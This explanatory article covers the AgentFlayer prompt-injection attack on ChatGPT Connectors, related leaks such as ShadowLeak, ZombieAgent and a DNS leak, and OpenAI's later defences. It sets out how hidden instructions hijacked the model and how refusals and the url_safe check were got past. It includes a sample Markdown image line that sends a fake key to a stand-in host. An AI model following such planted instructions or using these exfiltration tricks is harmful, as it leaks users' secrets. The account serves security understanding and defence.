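# AgentFlayer: the poisoned document that made ChatGPT leak data from Google Drive

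## ChatGPT Connectors, hidden instructions and the August 2025 demonstration

In August 2025, the Israeli security company Zenity gave the name AgentFlayer to a set of attacks on widely used AI assistants. In the demonstration of the best known attack, a user asks ChatGPT to summarise a document, unaware that it contains instructions in tiny white type. ChatGPT follows the instructions, searches the user's Google Drive for API keys (secret strings that give a program access to an online service) and sends the keys to the attacker. Michael Bargury and Tamir Ishay Sharbat of Zenity presented the attack on 6 August at Black Hat USA, a computer security conference in Las Vegas.

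The attack exploited a gap in OpenAI's checks on images and two ordinary properties of ChatGPT. By mid-2025, the chatbot could read private files in other services. Like other language models, it also could not reliably distinguish its user's instructions from instructions in the text it was reading.

### Connectors

ChatGPT's paying users could attach a file from Google Drive to a conversation as early as May 2024, but they had to pick the file themselves. A Connector, once switched on, let ChatGPT search a user's data in another service, read what it found and use it in an answer. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*, the technical post on the attack, describes a typical use, in which an employee asks ChatGPT a question about the company's personnel manuals on SharePoint, Microsoft's document store, instead of scrolling through them.

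OpenAI launched Connectors in beta on 4 June 2025, nine weeks before the talk. According to the release notes for its *ChatGPT Business* plan, ordinary chats could reach Google Drive, SharePoint, Dropbox and Box at launch. Deep research, a slower mode that produces long reports with citations, could also draw on Outlook, Gmail, Google Calendar, Microsoft Teams, GitHub, HubSpot and Linear. Canva and Notion followed in July.

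The June launch was for organisations on the Team, Enterprise and Edu plans. BGR reported that month that individual subscribers could use the Drive Connector in ordinary chats only on the $200-a-month Pro plan, and only outside the European Economic Area, Switzerland and the UK. Subscribers to the cheaper Plus plan could use Connectors in deep research, with the same regional exclusions, according to an OpenAI post that ForkLog (2025) reproduced. The people at risk from the Drive attack in August 2025 were therefore paying customers who had chosen to link their Drive, a much smaller group than all ChatGPT users.

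In the same post, OpenAI stressed that Connectors kept "existing user-level permissions", and TechRepublic's *ChatGPT Business Features Now Include Gmail/Outlook Connectors* repeated this assurance. ChatGPT can access only what the connected account can access, so an employee who cannot open the payroll folder cannot reach it through ChatGPT.

Permission checks keep employees out of other people's files. They don't protect an employee whose assistant is following an attacker's instructions, because the assistant's requests reach Google Drive with that employee's full rights. The API keys in Zenity's demonstration were in the victim's own Drive, so no permission check prevented the assistant from reading them.

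Five days after the talk, OpenAI made Teams, Outlook and GitHub available in ordinary chats. Two weeks later it added Gmail, Google Calendar and Google Contacts, which ChatGPT would consult whenever they seemed relevant, without the user selecting them each time.

OpenAI has since renamed connectors. On 18 December 2025 it moved them into a directory of "apps". OpenAI's *Connected apps in ChatGPT*, a help page from October 2026, calls them "connected apps" and says users set them up under a menu labelled Plugins. (OpenAI now uses "plugin" to mean a package that can bundle one or more apps with reusable skills.) At launch, organisations could have their Drive indexed in advance for faster answers. The OpenAI *ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu release notes* for October 2026 record that OpenAI ended this administrator-managed syncing in favour of live access.

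OpenAI's *Google Drive app and setup in ChatGPT* keeps the same permission rule, but the app can now do more. Where Google's permissions and the workspace's settings allow, ChatGPT can create, edit, move, share and delete files in Drive as well as read them. Users can also choose how often ChatGPT must ask before it reads something or acts.

### Instructions hidden in data

A language model takes in a single sequence of text and generates a continuation. When someone asks ChatGPT to summarise a file, that sequence includes OpenAI's standing instructions, the user's request and the file's contents. Formatting marks where each part starts, and training makes the model tend to give the user's words more weight than the file's. But nothing in the model prevents a sentence in the file from steering the answer as a sentence in the request would.

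A cook asks a chatbot to summarise a pancake recipe from a website. The recipe's author has added a line asking any AI that reads the page to finish with a joke about penguins, so the summary ends with one. This is a harmless example of **indirect prompt injection**, in which somebody places instructions in content that an AI model reads, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. It is "indirect" because the author of the instructions never types anything into the chat, and the user brings them in, usually without knowing it.

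Older software had a similar weakness. In SQL injection, a common hacking technique in the 1990s, an attacker typed database commands into a web form and the website's database ran them. SC Media's *Sloppy AI defenses take cybersecurity back to the 1990s, researchers say* (2025) reported that Rebecca Lynch, an Nvidia security researcher who also spoke at Black Hat that day, made this comparison. Lynch said that many language models, perhaps all, have trouble telling prompts from data, so an attacker mostly needs to find a place where outside text gets in.

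Unlike hidden instructions in a document, SQL injection has a known fix. Programmers use libraries that neutralise any special characters in a visitor's input before it reaches the database, and they can check by analysis that no path around those libraries exists. Bargury argued in *Why Aren't We Making Any Progress In Security From AI* (2025), an essay he posted about three weeks before the talk, that nobody can do this kind of analysis for a language model. An observer can see that a model fetched a document and then ran a web search, but cannot know whether the document's contents caused the search or whether pieces of the document ended up in the search terms. Bargury summarised the problem as "instructions are data". There are no special characters to neutralise, because a malicious instruction is made of the same ordinary words as everything else in the file.

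Models sometimes refuse planted instructions. In the same essay, Bargury showed GPT-4o, then one of the models behind ChatGPT, refusing, thanks to its training, to store a malicious memory that a Google Drive document had told it to store. Bargury calls training, filters and system instructions "soft boundaries" because they make bad behaviour less likely but don't rule it out. They are good enough against accidents but much less effective against an attacker, who can keep rewording the instruction until some version gets through.

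Bargury sells a remedy for this problem, but people without a product to sell describe it similarly. In NIST's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, technical staff at the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation wrote that many AI agents (systems that use a model to carry out tasks for a user) are vulnerable to hijacking.

### The Black Hat talk

Bargury is Zenity's co-founder and chief technology officer, and Sharbat was one of its threat researchers. Their session, "AI Enterprise Compromise: 0Click Exploit Methods", followed up on a talk Bargury had given at the same conference a year earlier, which showed how to turn Microsoft Copilot against the companies using it. He opened the 2025 session with the last slide of that talk and told the audience that the products had changed since then but had not got better. Bargury later wrote, in his notes on SC Media's report,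 that the two had squeezed 90 minutes of material into 40.

"AgentFlayer" covers everything Zenity released around that talk. The company's landing page, Zenity's *AgentFlayer* (2025), groups the attacks under six headings: ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot Studio, the coding tool Cursor when linked to the ticket tracker Jira, Salesforce Einstein, Google Gemini and Microsoft 365 Copilot. The Google Drive leak is one item under the first heading. The confusion is easy to understand, since Zenity Labs also put the name at the head of its post about the leak, and many readers will have met it only there. (AgentForger, a flaw in ChatGPT's tool for building agents that Zenity described in *One Click, One Attacker-Controlled Agentic Insider*, is a separate and later finding.)

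Zenity has a commercial interest in how alarming its findings sound, because it sells software for monitoring and controlling AI agents. The Jerusalem Post (2025) reported that the company had about 110 employees and that its clients included some of the largest American corporations. Its press release for the talk (Zenity, 2025) quotes the chief executive, Ben Kilger, as saying that current security approaches do not fit the way agents work and that this is why Zenity built its platform. The landing page ends with an invitation to book a demo.

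I would not discount the leak itself on that account, because the technical post describes the method in enough detail for OpenAI or anyone else to check it.

Zenity's commercial stake matters more for how the attacks were labelled. Its press release described the whole set as "0click", its spelling of zero-click, which means that an attack needs no mistaken action by the victim. The conference abstract, Black Hat's *AI Enterprise Compromise* (2025), was more precise, saying that some of the attacks need one bad click and others need none. Bargury's own list, *Pwn the Enterprise*, posted on 8 August, classes the Gemini and Microsoft 365 Copilot attacks as one-click, and The Decoder's *Agent-based AI systems face growing threats from zero-click and one-click exploits* (2025) kept the distinction. The Jerusalem Post reported that the ChatGPT attack worked without the user even opening a file,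 but in the version that Zenity Labs wrote up, the user uploads one.

### False memories

Bargury lists three video demonstrations against ChatGPT, one of which is the Drive leak. The other two exploit memory, the feature that carries information from a user's past conversations into later ones. In one, the attacker plants a false memory that leads ChatGPT to recommend a malicious software library when the victim later asks for a code snippet. In the other, a planted memory leads ChatGPT to persuade the victim to do something foolish.

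The leak takes secrets from the user's files and can do so in a single reply. A false memory can cause harm without taking any data, because it stays in the account and distorts the advice the user gets in conversations unrelated to the document, perhaps weeks later. Deleting the document would not remove the memory, so the user would have to find and delete it separately.

Zenity's broadest claim is that an attacker can take over a victim's ChatGPT completely, in the current conversation and all later ones. The part about later conversations rests on the memory demonstrations, not the Drive leak. Those demonstrations are also documented in less detail. The Zenity Labs post explains the leak step by step, while Bargury's list gives each memory attack a video and one sentence.

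Schneier on Security's *Hacking ChatGPT by Planting False Memories into Its Data* (2024) had already described a researcher's attack that planted memories in the ChatGPT app for macOS. The target told ChatGPT to view a web link that hosted a malicious image, and from then on the app sent everything the user typed and everything ChatGPT answered to the attacker's server. That attack combined a lasting memory with a data leak, while Zenity demonstrated the two separately.

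### Disclosure and bounties

Zenity privately reported the flaw to OpenAI before making it public, a practice known as "responsible disclosure" that gives the vendor a chance to fix the flaw first. In a press release dated the day of the talk, Zenity credited OpenAI and Microsoft with issuing patches after such disclosure. According to Zenity, other vendors declined to change anything and described the behaviour as intended.

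Bargury says OpenAI paid a bounty of $1,111 for the ChatGPT report and Microsoft paid $8,000 for the one on Copilot Studio. Each company sets its own scale for these rewards, so the difference is weak evidence about which flaw was worse. OpenAI's payment suggests that it accepted the report as a real security problem.

Bargury marked the ChatGPT attack as "fixed", but specified in brackets only that the injection Zenity had used no longer worked. He marked Microsoft's repair of Copilot Studio the same way, and said that an attacker could get around that block by rewording the instructions.

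## How the document made ChatGPT send out API keys

Zenity Labs got its instructions to ChatGPT through an uploaded document and got the stolen keys out by having ChatGPT display a picture. People use both features every day.

### The document and the request

Zenity hid its instructions to ChatGPT in an ordinary-looking document, using white letters one pixel high, so a person scrolling through the page would see only blank space where they were. ChatGPT works from the text extracted from a file, where colour and size no longer matter, so it receives the hidden lines in the same way as the visible ones. TechSpot, a technology news site, reported that the hidden text was 300 words long.

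In the version Zenity Labs wrote up, the victim uploads this file to ChatGPT and asks for a summary. People do the same with CVs, contracts and reports from outside their company, so an attacker only has to wait for someone to do it with the poisoned file. An attacker inside the company would have a better chance. Zenity Labs points out that a malicious employee could add hidden text to every document they can access, or send colleagues long, trustworthy-looking files that those colleagues would probably upload to ChatGPT rather than read.

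### What the hidden text was for

ChatGPT now had a file and a request to summarise it. For the attack to work, the hidden text had to make ChatGPT drop that request and follow another without alarming the user.

The first lines imitated the markers that show where a file's contents end. The document appeared to be over and a separate set of instructions seemed to begin, so the text that followed seemed to come from someone with more authority than the file's author. This can work because the model does not verify such markers.

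Zenity then withdrew the request for a summary by claiming the user had made it by mistake. Without this step, ChatGPT would have had two competing tasks, the user's visible request and Zenity's instructions.

Next, the document told a story in which the user was a developer with a deadline that day, whose team was waiting for API keys stored somewhere in the developer's own Drive. Models tend to refuse requests involving passwords and keys, and Zenity Labs says the story was meant to overcome this. It gave the search an innocent explanation, since people do lose track of their own keys. Zenity's researchers had a similar problem with the coding tool Cursor, which refused a plain request to find API keys. According to *Sloppy AI defenses take cybersecurity back to the 1990s, researchers say*, Cursor complied once they described what the keys looked like and called them something else.

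Zenity's hidden text next instructed ChatGPT to search Google Drive for the keys and ignore the current document, probably because that text mentioned API keys so often that a search might have stopped there. ChatGPT was then to write the keys into the web address of an image. Zenity gave a pretext for this odd format too, describing the image as a placeholder in the project's documentation.

To hide the attack, the remaining lines told ChatGPT to keep its answer short, not mention the search or the change of plan, and end with a friendly phrase. They also told it not to use code formatting, which would have made the chat window show the image's address as text instead of loading the image.

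### How a picture can carry a key

The victim had already connected Google Drive, so the search needed no new login or further click. ChatGPT found the keys and put them in its reply in the form the document specified.

ChatGPT writes its replies in Markdown, a simple notation that the chat window turns into headings, bold type, links and pictures. A Markdown image consists of a caption and a web address. With an invented address and a fake key, it might look like this:

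`![Sales chart](https://pictures.example/chart.png?note=FAKE-KEY-12345)`

The user never sees this line. The chat window reads it, fetches the picture from pictures.example and shows a sales chart in its place.

Everything before the question mark identifies the file. What follows is a parameter, a slot for extra information that websites use for such things as the size of a picture. A server with no use for the parameter can ignore it and send the chart anyway. But the user's browser has to send the full address to get the chart, and servers commonly log the requests they receive. The owner of pictures.example would find an entry like this one:

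`10:42:07 GET /chart.png?note=FAKE-KEY-12345`

The fake key has now left the user's computer. The browser did nothing unusual, since it makes requests like this for every web page with pictures. On an ordinary page, the author sets the image addresses in advance, but here a language model wrote the address after reading the user's private files.

The request goes out as soon as the picture loads, so the user does not need to click on it, and closing the conversation afterwards does not undo the leak. The picture can also be hard to notice. According to *Pwn the Enterprise*, the one in the video demonstration was a single transparent pixel.

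This trick predates Zenity's attack. The software developer Simon Willison, who collects such cases on his blog, calls it "Markdown exfiltration" and describes it as a common way to get private data out of chatbots.

### The blocked address and the detour

Zenity's first attempt failed. The image address pointed to a service that developers use to test web requests. Before loading the image, the chat window submitted the address to url_safe, OpenAI's check on where images may come from. The check rejected the address, so the image did not load and the keys did not reach Zenity.

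This failure came late in the chain. ChatGPT must already have followed the hidden text far enough to write the image line, or url_safe would have had no address to reject. The model's training had not stopped the attack, so Zenity only had to find an address that the check would accept.

It found one on a major cloud provider's storage service. Anyone who opens an account can rent space there, and customers' files share the provider's well-known domain. Account holders can also log each request for their files, including any parameters in the address. These logs have ordinary uses, such as finding out why a download failed.

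Zenity stored a harmless picture in its own account with the provider and pointed the hidden text at it. This time url_safe allowed the address, the picture appeared in the chat, and the keys appeared in Zenity's log. The provider was trustworthy, but that didn't guarantee its customers were, and the attacker was one of them. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes the same workaround, which the security researcher Johann Rehberger found independently.

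Other companies' lists of trusted sites have had similar flaws. In one case Willison records, Google's coding tool Antigravity allowed its browser to visit only approved sites by default, but the list included a service where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. In another, Salesforce still trusted a domain whose registration had lapsed, and researchers bought it and received the leaked data there.

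### Was it "zero-click"?

A zero-click attack usually means one that works without any action by the victim. FORCEDENTRY, a well-known example discovered in 2021, could install the spyware Pegasus on an iPhone without its owner touching anything. Attackers prize such attacks because caution doesn't protect the victim, who has little chance of noticing.

In its press release for AgentFlayer, Zenity wrote that the attacks needed no "user action" and that the one on ChatGPT was "email-triggered". On its landing page, Zenity Labs claimed that the attacks overall needed no user action only "in several scenarios", but said the ChatGPT attack needed just an email address and no user input.

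The written demonstration does not fit that description, because the attack depends on the victim uploading a file and asking ChatGPT to summarise it. Zenity Labs says in the same post that no additional clicks are required, but it is referring to what happens after the upload.

A second version of the attack probably used the email address. According to SecurityWeek's *Major Enterprise AI Assistants Can Be Abused for Data Theft, Manipulation*, the attacker shared the poisoned file with the victim and needed only the victim's email address to do so. This would explain the press release's wording, because Google Drive lets people share a file by entering the recipient's address. The victim didn't have to upload the file in this version, but SecurityWeek also reported that the hidden instructions took effect only when the victim told ChatGPT to process it.

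The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data* describes an attack in which the victim's request did not mention the file. Once the document was in the victim's Drive, a question such as "Summarize my last meeting with Sam" could be enough to trigger it. ChatGPT's search for notes on the meeting would have to bring up the poisoned document, so the attacker would need to guess what the victim was likely to ask about. This version is the most worrying because the victim never chooses the file and may not know that it exists. It is also less well documented than the upload. The Zenity Labs post does not explain it step by step, although SC Media's reporter, who attended the talk, described the malicious prompts as coming from Google Drive.

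Several news reports left out or played down the victim's request to ChatGPT. Sharon Goldman (2025), in *Hacker, bodyguard, target*, wrote in Fortune that the attack required "no clicks or downloads". TechSpot called it a true zero-click threat, then explained that ChatGPT would send out the keys the next time the victim used it.

Bargury uses a different definition, based on whether the victim makes a mistake. In *Pwn the Enterprise*, he calls an attack "1click" if the user must do one ill-advised thing, such as clicking a link, and "0click" if the user has "nothing tangible they can do to protect themselves". He classes his attack on Google Gemini as one-click because, although the victim also starts with a harmless question, the harm comes only when they act on Gemini's bad advice, for instance by clicking a phishing link.

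Zenity did not keep to this definition. Its landing page explains "0click" as "no user interaction", as does WHY2025's *0click Enterprise compromise* (2025), the abstract of a talk another Zenity researcher gave on 9 August. Zenity Labs' undated post *AI Agents & 0-Click Exploits* was stricter still, reserving the term for agents that act without the user's intervention. It said that assistants that mostly read data and answer questions suffered almost exclusively from one-click attacks.

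A neutral scale helps here. CERT/CC's *User Interaction*, a page from an American centre that coordinates reports of software flaws, gives the three grades used in CVSS, the standard system for scoring how severe such flaws are:

- **None:** the attack works without any human except the attacker.
- **Passive:** the victim has limited, involuntary contact with the attacker's material and does not override any protection.
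- **Active:** the victim takes specific, conscious steps involving the attacker's material, or undermines a protection.

Uploading the poisoned file and asking about it looks like active interaction, even though the victim does not know what the file contains. The version with the question about Sam fits the passive grade, so neither version qualifies as "none".

Zenity's attack on Microsoft Copilot Studio does qualify, because no employee had to open a message or ask a question. Sharbat sent emails to a customer-service agent that Zenity had modelled on one used by McKinsey, and the agent emailed back records from a customer database.

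The evidence therefore supports a narrower claim than the press release's: someone doing ordinary work with ChatGPT could lose API keys without clicking a suspicious link or approving anything unusual. Even Bargury's definition doesn't quite fit the upload version, because a user could refuse to upload files from strangers or disconnect Google Drive first. But reading other people's documents is one of ChatGPT's main uses, and a user who takes these precautions gives up much of the product. Bargury's description is more accurate when the file arrives by sharing, since disconnecting Drive is then the only obvious precaution left.

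The looser meaning has since spread. Adversa AI's *Top 10 zero-click attacks against AI agents* applies the term to attacks in which victims do nothing outside their normal workflow. In August 2026, SecurityWeek's *Zero-Click AI Browser Hacking* used it for a Zenity attack that begins when a user asks Claude, Anthropic's assistant, to summarise recent emails. An attack on an AI assistant that is described as "zero-click" may therefore still require the victim to ask the assistant something.

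### What was taken, and from whom

The keys came from a demonstration account. Zenity calls the ChatGPT attack a "simulation" on its landing page, and The Decoder calls it a proof of concept. The flaw was real, because the attack ran against OpenAI's actual product, but Zenity chose the victim's files and knew they contained keys. An attacker who sent the same document to strangers could steal keys only from those who had connected a Drive with keys stored in it.

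The Zenity Labs post shows one successful run and gives no success rate. A language model can respond differently to the same text each time, so one success shows that the attack was possible but not how often it would have worked. Zenity Labs says that an attacker could target SharePoint, GitHub or any other connected service in the same way. This is plausible because the hidden text would need little change, but the post demonstrates theft only from Google Drive.

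The Decoder reported that the attack could not transfer entire documents, and TechSpot reported that it could extract only a limited amount of data per request. This was because the stolen data had to fit in the image's web address, and browsers and servers limit the length of addresses. A contract or a spreadsheet would usually be too long.

An API key is a good target for this method because it is short enough to fit easily within the size limit, and whoever holds it may be able to read a company's database or run up charges on its account. The limit therefore protected the victim's documents much better than it protected the systems whose keys were in those documents.

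The attacker steered one ChatGPT reply and received the data it sent out, but did not obtain the victim's password and could not log in to the account. Ynetnews' *In first, Israeli cybersecurity firm exposes ChatGPT vulnerability* incorrectly reported that the attacker gained full control of the account.

Nobody has publicly identified a real victim of the attack. Zenity's chief executive said in the company's press release that attackers were "already exploiting these systems in production", but he was talking about AI agents in general and gave no example. *ChatGPT Connectors Vulnerability Enables Zero-Click Data Theft via Poisoned Documents*, an entry in the OECD's public database of AI incidents, classes the case as an incident, and its AI-generated explanation refers to "realized harm". But the explanation doesn't identify a victim, and it bases that judgement on Zenity's demonstration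 and the possibility that someone could have used the method maliciously.

Google told SecurityWeek in August 2025 that prompt injection was rarely seen in real attacks. In 2026 Google searched a large archive of public web pages for known injection patterns. *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* (2026) quotes Google as saying it did not see "significant amounts of advanced attacks", such as those using the exfiltration prompts that security researchers had published in 2025. Google took this as a sign that attackers had not yet used the research at scale.

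That is somewhat reassuring about the open web, but the search could not have found a poisoned file that an attacker shared privately through Google Drive. Victims would also have had trouble noticing the theft. They would have seen a short, friendly reply instead of the summary they had asked for, and perhaps a small picture. If someone later misused a stolen key, its owner would have had little reason to connect the misuse with that conversation.

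## How OpenAI tried to stop leaks through web addresses

Johann Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI in early April 2023, more than two years before Zenity's talk. OpenAI did not yet pay for reports of security flaws, so he argued his case by email. He recalls in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that the company showed little interest in fixing the problem. He also told Microsoft, whose Bing Chat leaked data in the same way. Microsoft closed the leak in May 2023 with a Content-Security-Policy, a set of rules a website sends to the browser to limit where it can load images and other material from.

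OpenAI followed in December. Rehberger had just given a live demonstration that sent details of a consenting volunteer's conversation to his server. The next day, he found that ChatGPT's website had begun refusing some images. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* explains why. When a reply contained an image, the chat window now sent the image's address to url_safe, a checking service on OpenAI's servers, and fetched the image only if the service returned "safe". Rehberger tested a web address with an email address attached, and url_safe rejected it.

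### A check with secret rules

Rehberger welcomed url_safe but objected to its secrecy. Anyone can read a website's Content-Security-Policy in their own browser, but only OpenAI knew how url_safe classified URLs. He tested it with 36 images on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them loaded. He could see no reason why the image for "a" loaded but the one for "d" did not. He still managed to send the word "hi" to his server by having ChatGPT load one image per letter.

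The check also didn't cover every version of ChatGPT. OpenAI had built it into the website's chat window, so every other version needed its own copy. The iPhone app didn't have one, and neither did the macOS app, where the false-memory attack of 2024 took place. Rehberger suggested running the check on OpenAI's servers, where it would protect every version, and limiting the number of images in a reply.

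Outsiders spent the next two years trying to infer the rules. The security company Tenable ran experiments and concluded in *HackedGPT* that url_safe's result depended on whether the domain and any subdomain were trusted, whether the address had parameters, and what the conversation had been about. If the result depended heavily on the domain, an attacker could look for a trusted domain that would accept data from anyone.

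Rehberger found two domains that could be used to get around url_safe. One belonged to Microsoft's cloud storage service, Azure Blob Storage, and the other to Apache, a foundation that publishes free software. He says he told OpenAI in October 2024 about several ways around url_safe, including the cloud storage method that Zenity later used. Cyber Security News' *ChatGPT "0-Click" Connectors Vulnerability* also names Azure Blob Storage in its account of Zenity's attack.

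In the month before he published, Rehberger asked OpenAI several times whether it had fixed the problem and got no update. He published on 1 August 2025 (the date given in Willison's *The Summer of Johann*), five days before Zenity's talk. His demonstration stole a user's recent chat history instead of Google Drive files, and he withheld the exact prompt because the vulnerability still wasn't fixed.

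If Rehberger's dates are right, OpenAI had about ten months' notice of the weakness that Zenity used to leak the keys. This is his own account, but it is consistent with how OpenAI handled another report. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) describes a different way around the check, which OpenAI had also not resolved when Tenable published the advisory.

### What "fixed" meant in August 2025

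When Bargury described the problem as "fixed," he was referring only to the injection. That fix alone would not have stopped an attacker who reworded the injection from sending API keys to the same storage service as before.

Rehberger says that OpenAI made a second repair around August 2025 by strengthening url_safe, and that this stopped the attacks shown at Black Hat as well as his own. Shortly before publishing, he had noticed that the chat window no longer made a visible call to url_safe, which he took as a sign that OpenAI was changing something. Bargury's list does not mention the change, but it would be the more valuable repair, because an attacker cannot make a blocked address load by rewording the document.

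### Only addresses that are already public

OpenAI explained its new approach on 28 January 2026 in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* and an accompanying technical paper. An address may load automatically only if it already exists in public, independently of any user's conversation. OpenAI checks this with a crawler, a program that follows links across the public web and records the addresses it finds, as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to conversations or accounts, so it cannot record an address that ChatGPT has just composed from somebody's private files.

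Before ChatGPT automatically fetches a page or an image, OpenAI compares the full address with the crawler's records. If the address matches exactly, ChatGPT fetches it. If not, ChatGPT either looks for another site or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. As far as Rehberger can tell, addresses that users type into the chat also count as safe for that conversation.

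This rule would stop the AgentFlayer image. In the earlier example of a sales chart on pictures.example, the crawler might well have recorded `chart.png` if a public page displayed it, but it could not have recorded `chart.png?note=FAKE-KEY-12345`, because nobody had written that address until ChatGPT put the victim's key into it. The picture therefore would not load automatically, however reputable the storage provider was.

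OpenAI gave two reasons for not simply keeping a list of trusted sites. First, many respectable sites forward visitors elsewhere, so a link can begin on a trusted domain and end on the attacker's. Second, a list strict enough to be safe would set off frequent false alarms, and people would learn to click through the warnings without reading them.

Tenable had found an example of the first problem. Bing's search results use bing.com links that forward the visitor to the actual site, and url_safe always accepted bing.com, so any site in Bing's index had a trusted address. Tenable could not add data to these links, so it had Bing index a separate page for each letter and spelled out the stolen text with the links to those pages.

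OpenAI's post does not discuss the simpler weakness that Zenity used, which needed no forwarding at all.

By March 2026 OpenAI was calling the safeguard Safe Url. OpenAI says in *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) that most attempts to make ChatGPT send out secrets fail because its training leads it to refuse. Safe Url is for cases where the model has been deceived. It either blocks the transmission or shows the user what would leave the conversation and asks for confirmation. OpenAI applies it to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, its web browser, and to searches and page visits in deep research. Small applications that run inside ChatGPT have a similar safeguard.

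Because users can choose to confirm an address, the protection depends partly on their judgement. Someone in a hurry may approve an address without noticing the string of characters at its end. OpenAI worried about this habit when it argued against lists.

One outside test suggests that ChatGPT's protections as a whole work against prepared attacks. *The Framing Gap* (August 2026) tested planted instructions meant to make a model give away a confidential value. A model reached through OpenAI's programming interface, without the ChatGPT product around it, leaked the value in up to 100% of trials for some wordings. ChatGPT itself leaked it in none of 48 valid trials. The researchers could not see inside the product, so they don't say whether training, Safe Url or something else made the difference. Even if the trials were a fair sample, 48 without a leak would be compatible with a true leak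 rate of up to about 6%, and an attacker can try other wordings.

### Requests from OpenAI's own servers

In 2025 url_safe checked addresses only in images and links that were about to appear on the user's screen, but ChatGPT could also open web pages itself, from OpenAI's servers.

The security company Radware used this second route in an attack it called ShadowLeak. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an email about a company restructuring, with instructions that could be hidden in tiny or white type, as in Zenity's document. When the victim asked deep research to go through the day's emails, deep research read the instructions, found an employee's name and address in another message, and opened a web address on the attacker's server with those details added to it. Radware saw no limit like url_safe on where deep research could send requests.

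Nothing appeared on the victim's screen, and the victim's employer could not have caught the request because it never passed through the company's computers or network. AgentFlayer's request, by contrast, came from the victim's browser, so a company that monitored its employees' web traffic might have noticed it.

ShadowLeak did not work at first. Deep research refused plain instructions to send out personal data, then refused the same instructions when they were presented as a user's request. Telling it to retry after failures helped somewhat, but it sometimes opened the web address without the data. Radware then told it to encode the data in Base64, a standard way of turning data into an unreadable string, and described this as a security measure. The company reports that this worked every time in repeated tests.

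In its March 2026 post, OpenAI reports a lower success rate of 50%. The post reprints part of an email with the same wording and credits unnamed outside researchers. The two rates may come from different versions of the email or of ChatGPT.

Radware reported ShadowLeak on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, and acknowledged it on 3 September. Radware (2025) announced it publicly on 18 September.

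### Spelling out a secret

After these attacks, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to an address it had been given. Radware's next attack, ZombieAgent, worked within that restriction. According to Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the malicious email supplied a complete address for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT opened them one after another to spell the stolen text. Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also made separate addresses for each position in the text, which means 360 addresses for ten positions.

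Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* dates Radware's public report to 8 January 2026, less than three weeks before OpenAI explained the public-address rule.

Radware also found a gap in how OpenAI handled memory. OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from using memory in a chat after it had used a Connector, presumably so that an email could not plant a lasting instruction. But ChatGPT could still read its memories first and then use a Connector. A poisoned file that the user shared once could therefore save a rule in memory telling ChatGPT to find the attacker's email and follow its instructions before answering any message.

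Spelling is still possible under the public-address rule, but it is harder because the attacker's addresses must already be in the crawler's records. Rehberger notes that anyone with a reasonably large website probably has 36 recorded pages, and can decide that one stands for A, another for B and so on. The pages are public and harmless, but the attacker can work out the secret from which ones ChatGPT opens and in what order. OpenAI acknowledges this method in its technical paper.

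Under the rule, stealing a 40-character API key would take 40 page visits instead of a single image request. Many keys also distinguish capital letters from small ones, so 36 pages would not be enough. The extra visits make the theft easier for OpenAI to notice and more likely to fail. Rehberger suggests also preventing ChatGPT from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make the theft harder still. But an attacker who needs only one key may be patient, and a yes-or-no fact about the user, such as whether a certain file exists, could leak in a single visit.

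He also doubts that every team at OpenAI will remember to use the safeguard in each new feature. That worry is reasonable, because the checks were missing from the phone apps and deep research.

### A leak without a web address in the chat

In March 2026 the security company Check Point described a leak that no check of the web addresses in a conversation would have caught. ChatGPT can write and run small programs, for instance to analyse a spreadsheet, in an environment that OpenAI had cut off from the internet. But Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) explains that these programs could still use DNS, the system that computers use to look up the numerical address behind a name such as example.com.

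A lookup passes the requested name along a chain of servers, and the domain's owner can control the last one. The owner can therefore read any data placed in the name, even if no web page loads. Check Point built a customised version of ChatGPT that acted as a personal doctor and gave it a patient's test results. The patient's name and the medical assessment reached Check Point's server, while ChatGPT told the user that it had not sent the data anywhere. The model operated as if its environment were sealed, so it did not treat a lookup as sending data out.

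Unlike AgentFlayer, this attack began when the victim pasted in a malicious prompt, perhaps one advertised as a productivity trick, or opened a customised ChatGPT that an attacker had built. OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem itself, and finished fixing it on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw maliciously.

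Check Point found another route that September, again in the environment where ChatGPT runs code. According to OffSeq's *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox* (2026), a shared internal service for delivering software packages let one account's environment pass messages to another's. An attacker could use it to run hidden tasks in a victim's session, with access to the victim's connected tools and data.

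### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's broadest measure was Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that lets users turn off most of the routes through which data could leak at once. OpenAI announced it on 13 February 2026 in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. It was meant for a small group of people with high security needs, such as executives. At first only organisations on the Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans could use it. On 4 June OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to Business accounts that customers manage themselves. Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* confirms that this included the free plan.

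With Lockdown Mode on, ChatGPT reads stored copies of web pages instead of visiting the live ones. It may not show images in ordinary replies, and it can't download files for analysis. Deep research is unavailable, and so is agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. Code that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editing window, can't connect to the network. Lockdown Mode does not restrict network access for Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant.

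In Lockdown Mode, people can still upload files, and ChatGPT can still use its memory. OpenAI acknowledges on its help page, *Lockdown Mode*, that a poisoned document could therefore reach the model and distort its answer. But the AgentFlayer document could not leak the key by getting a picture to load.

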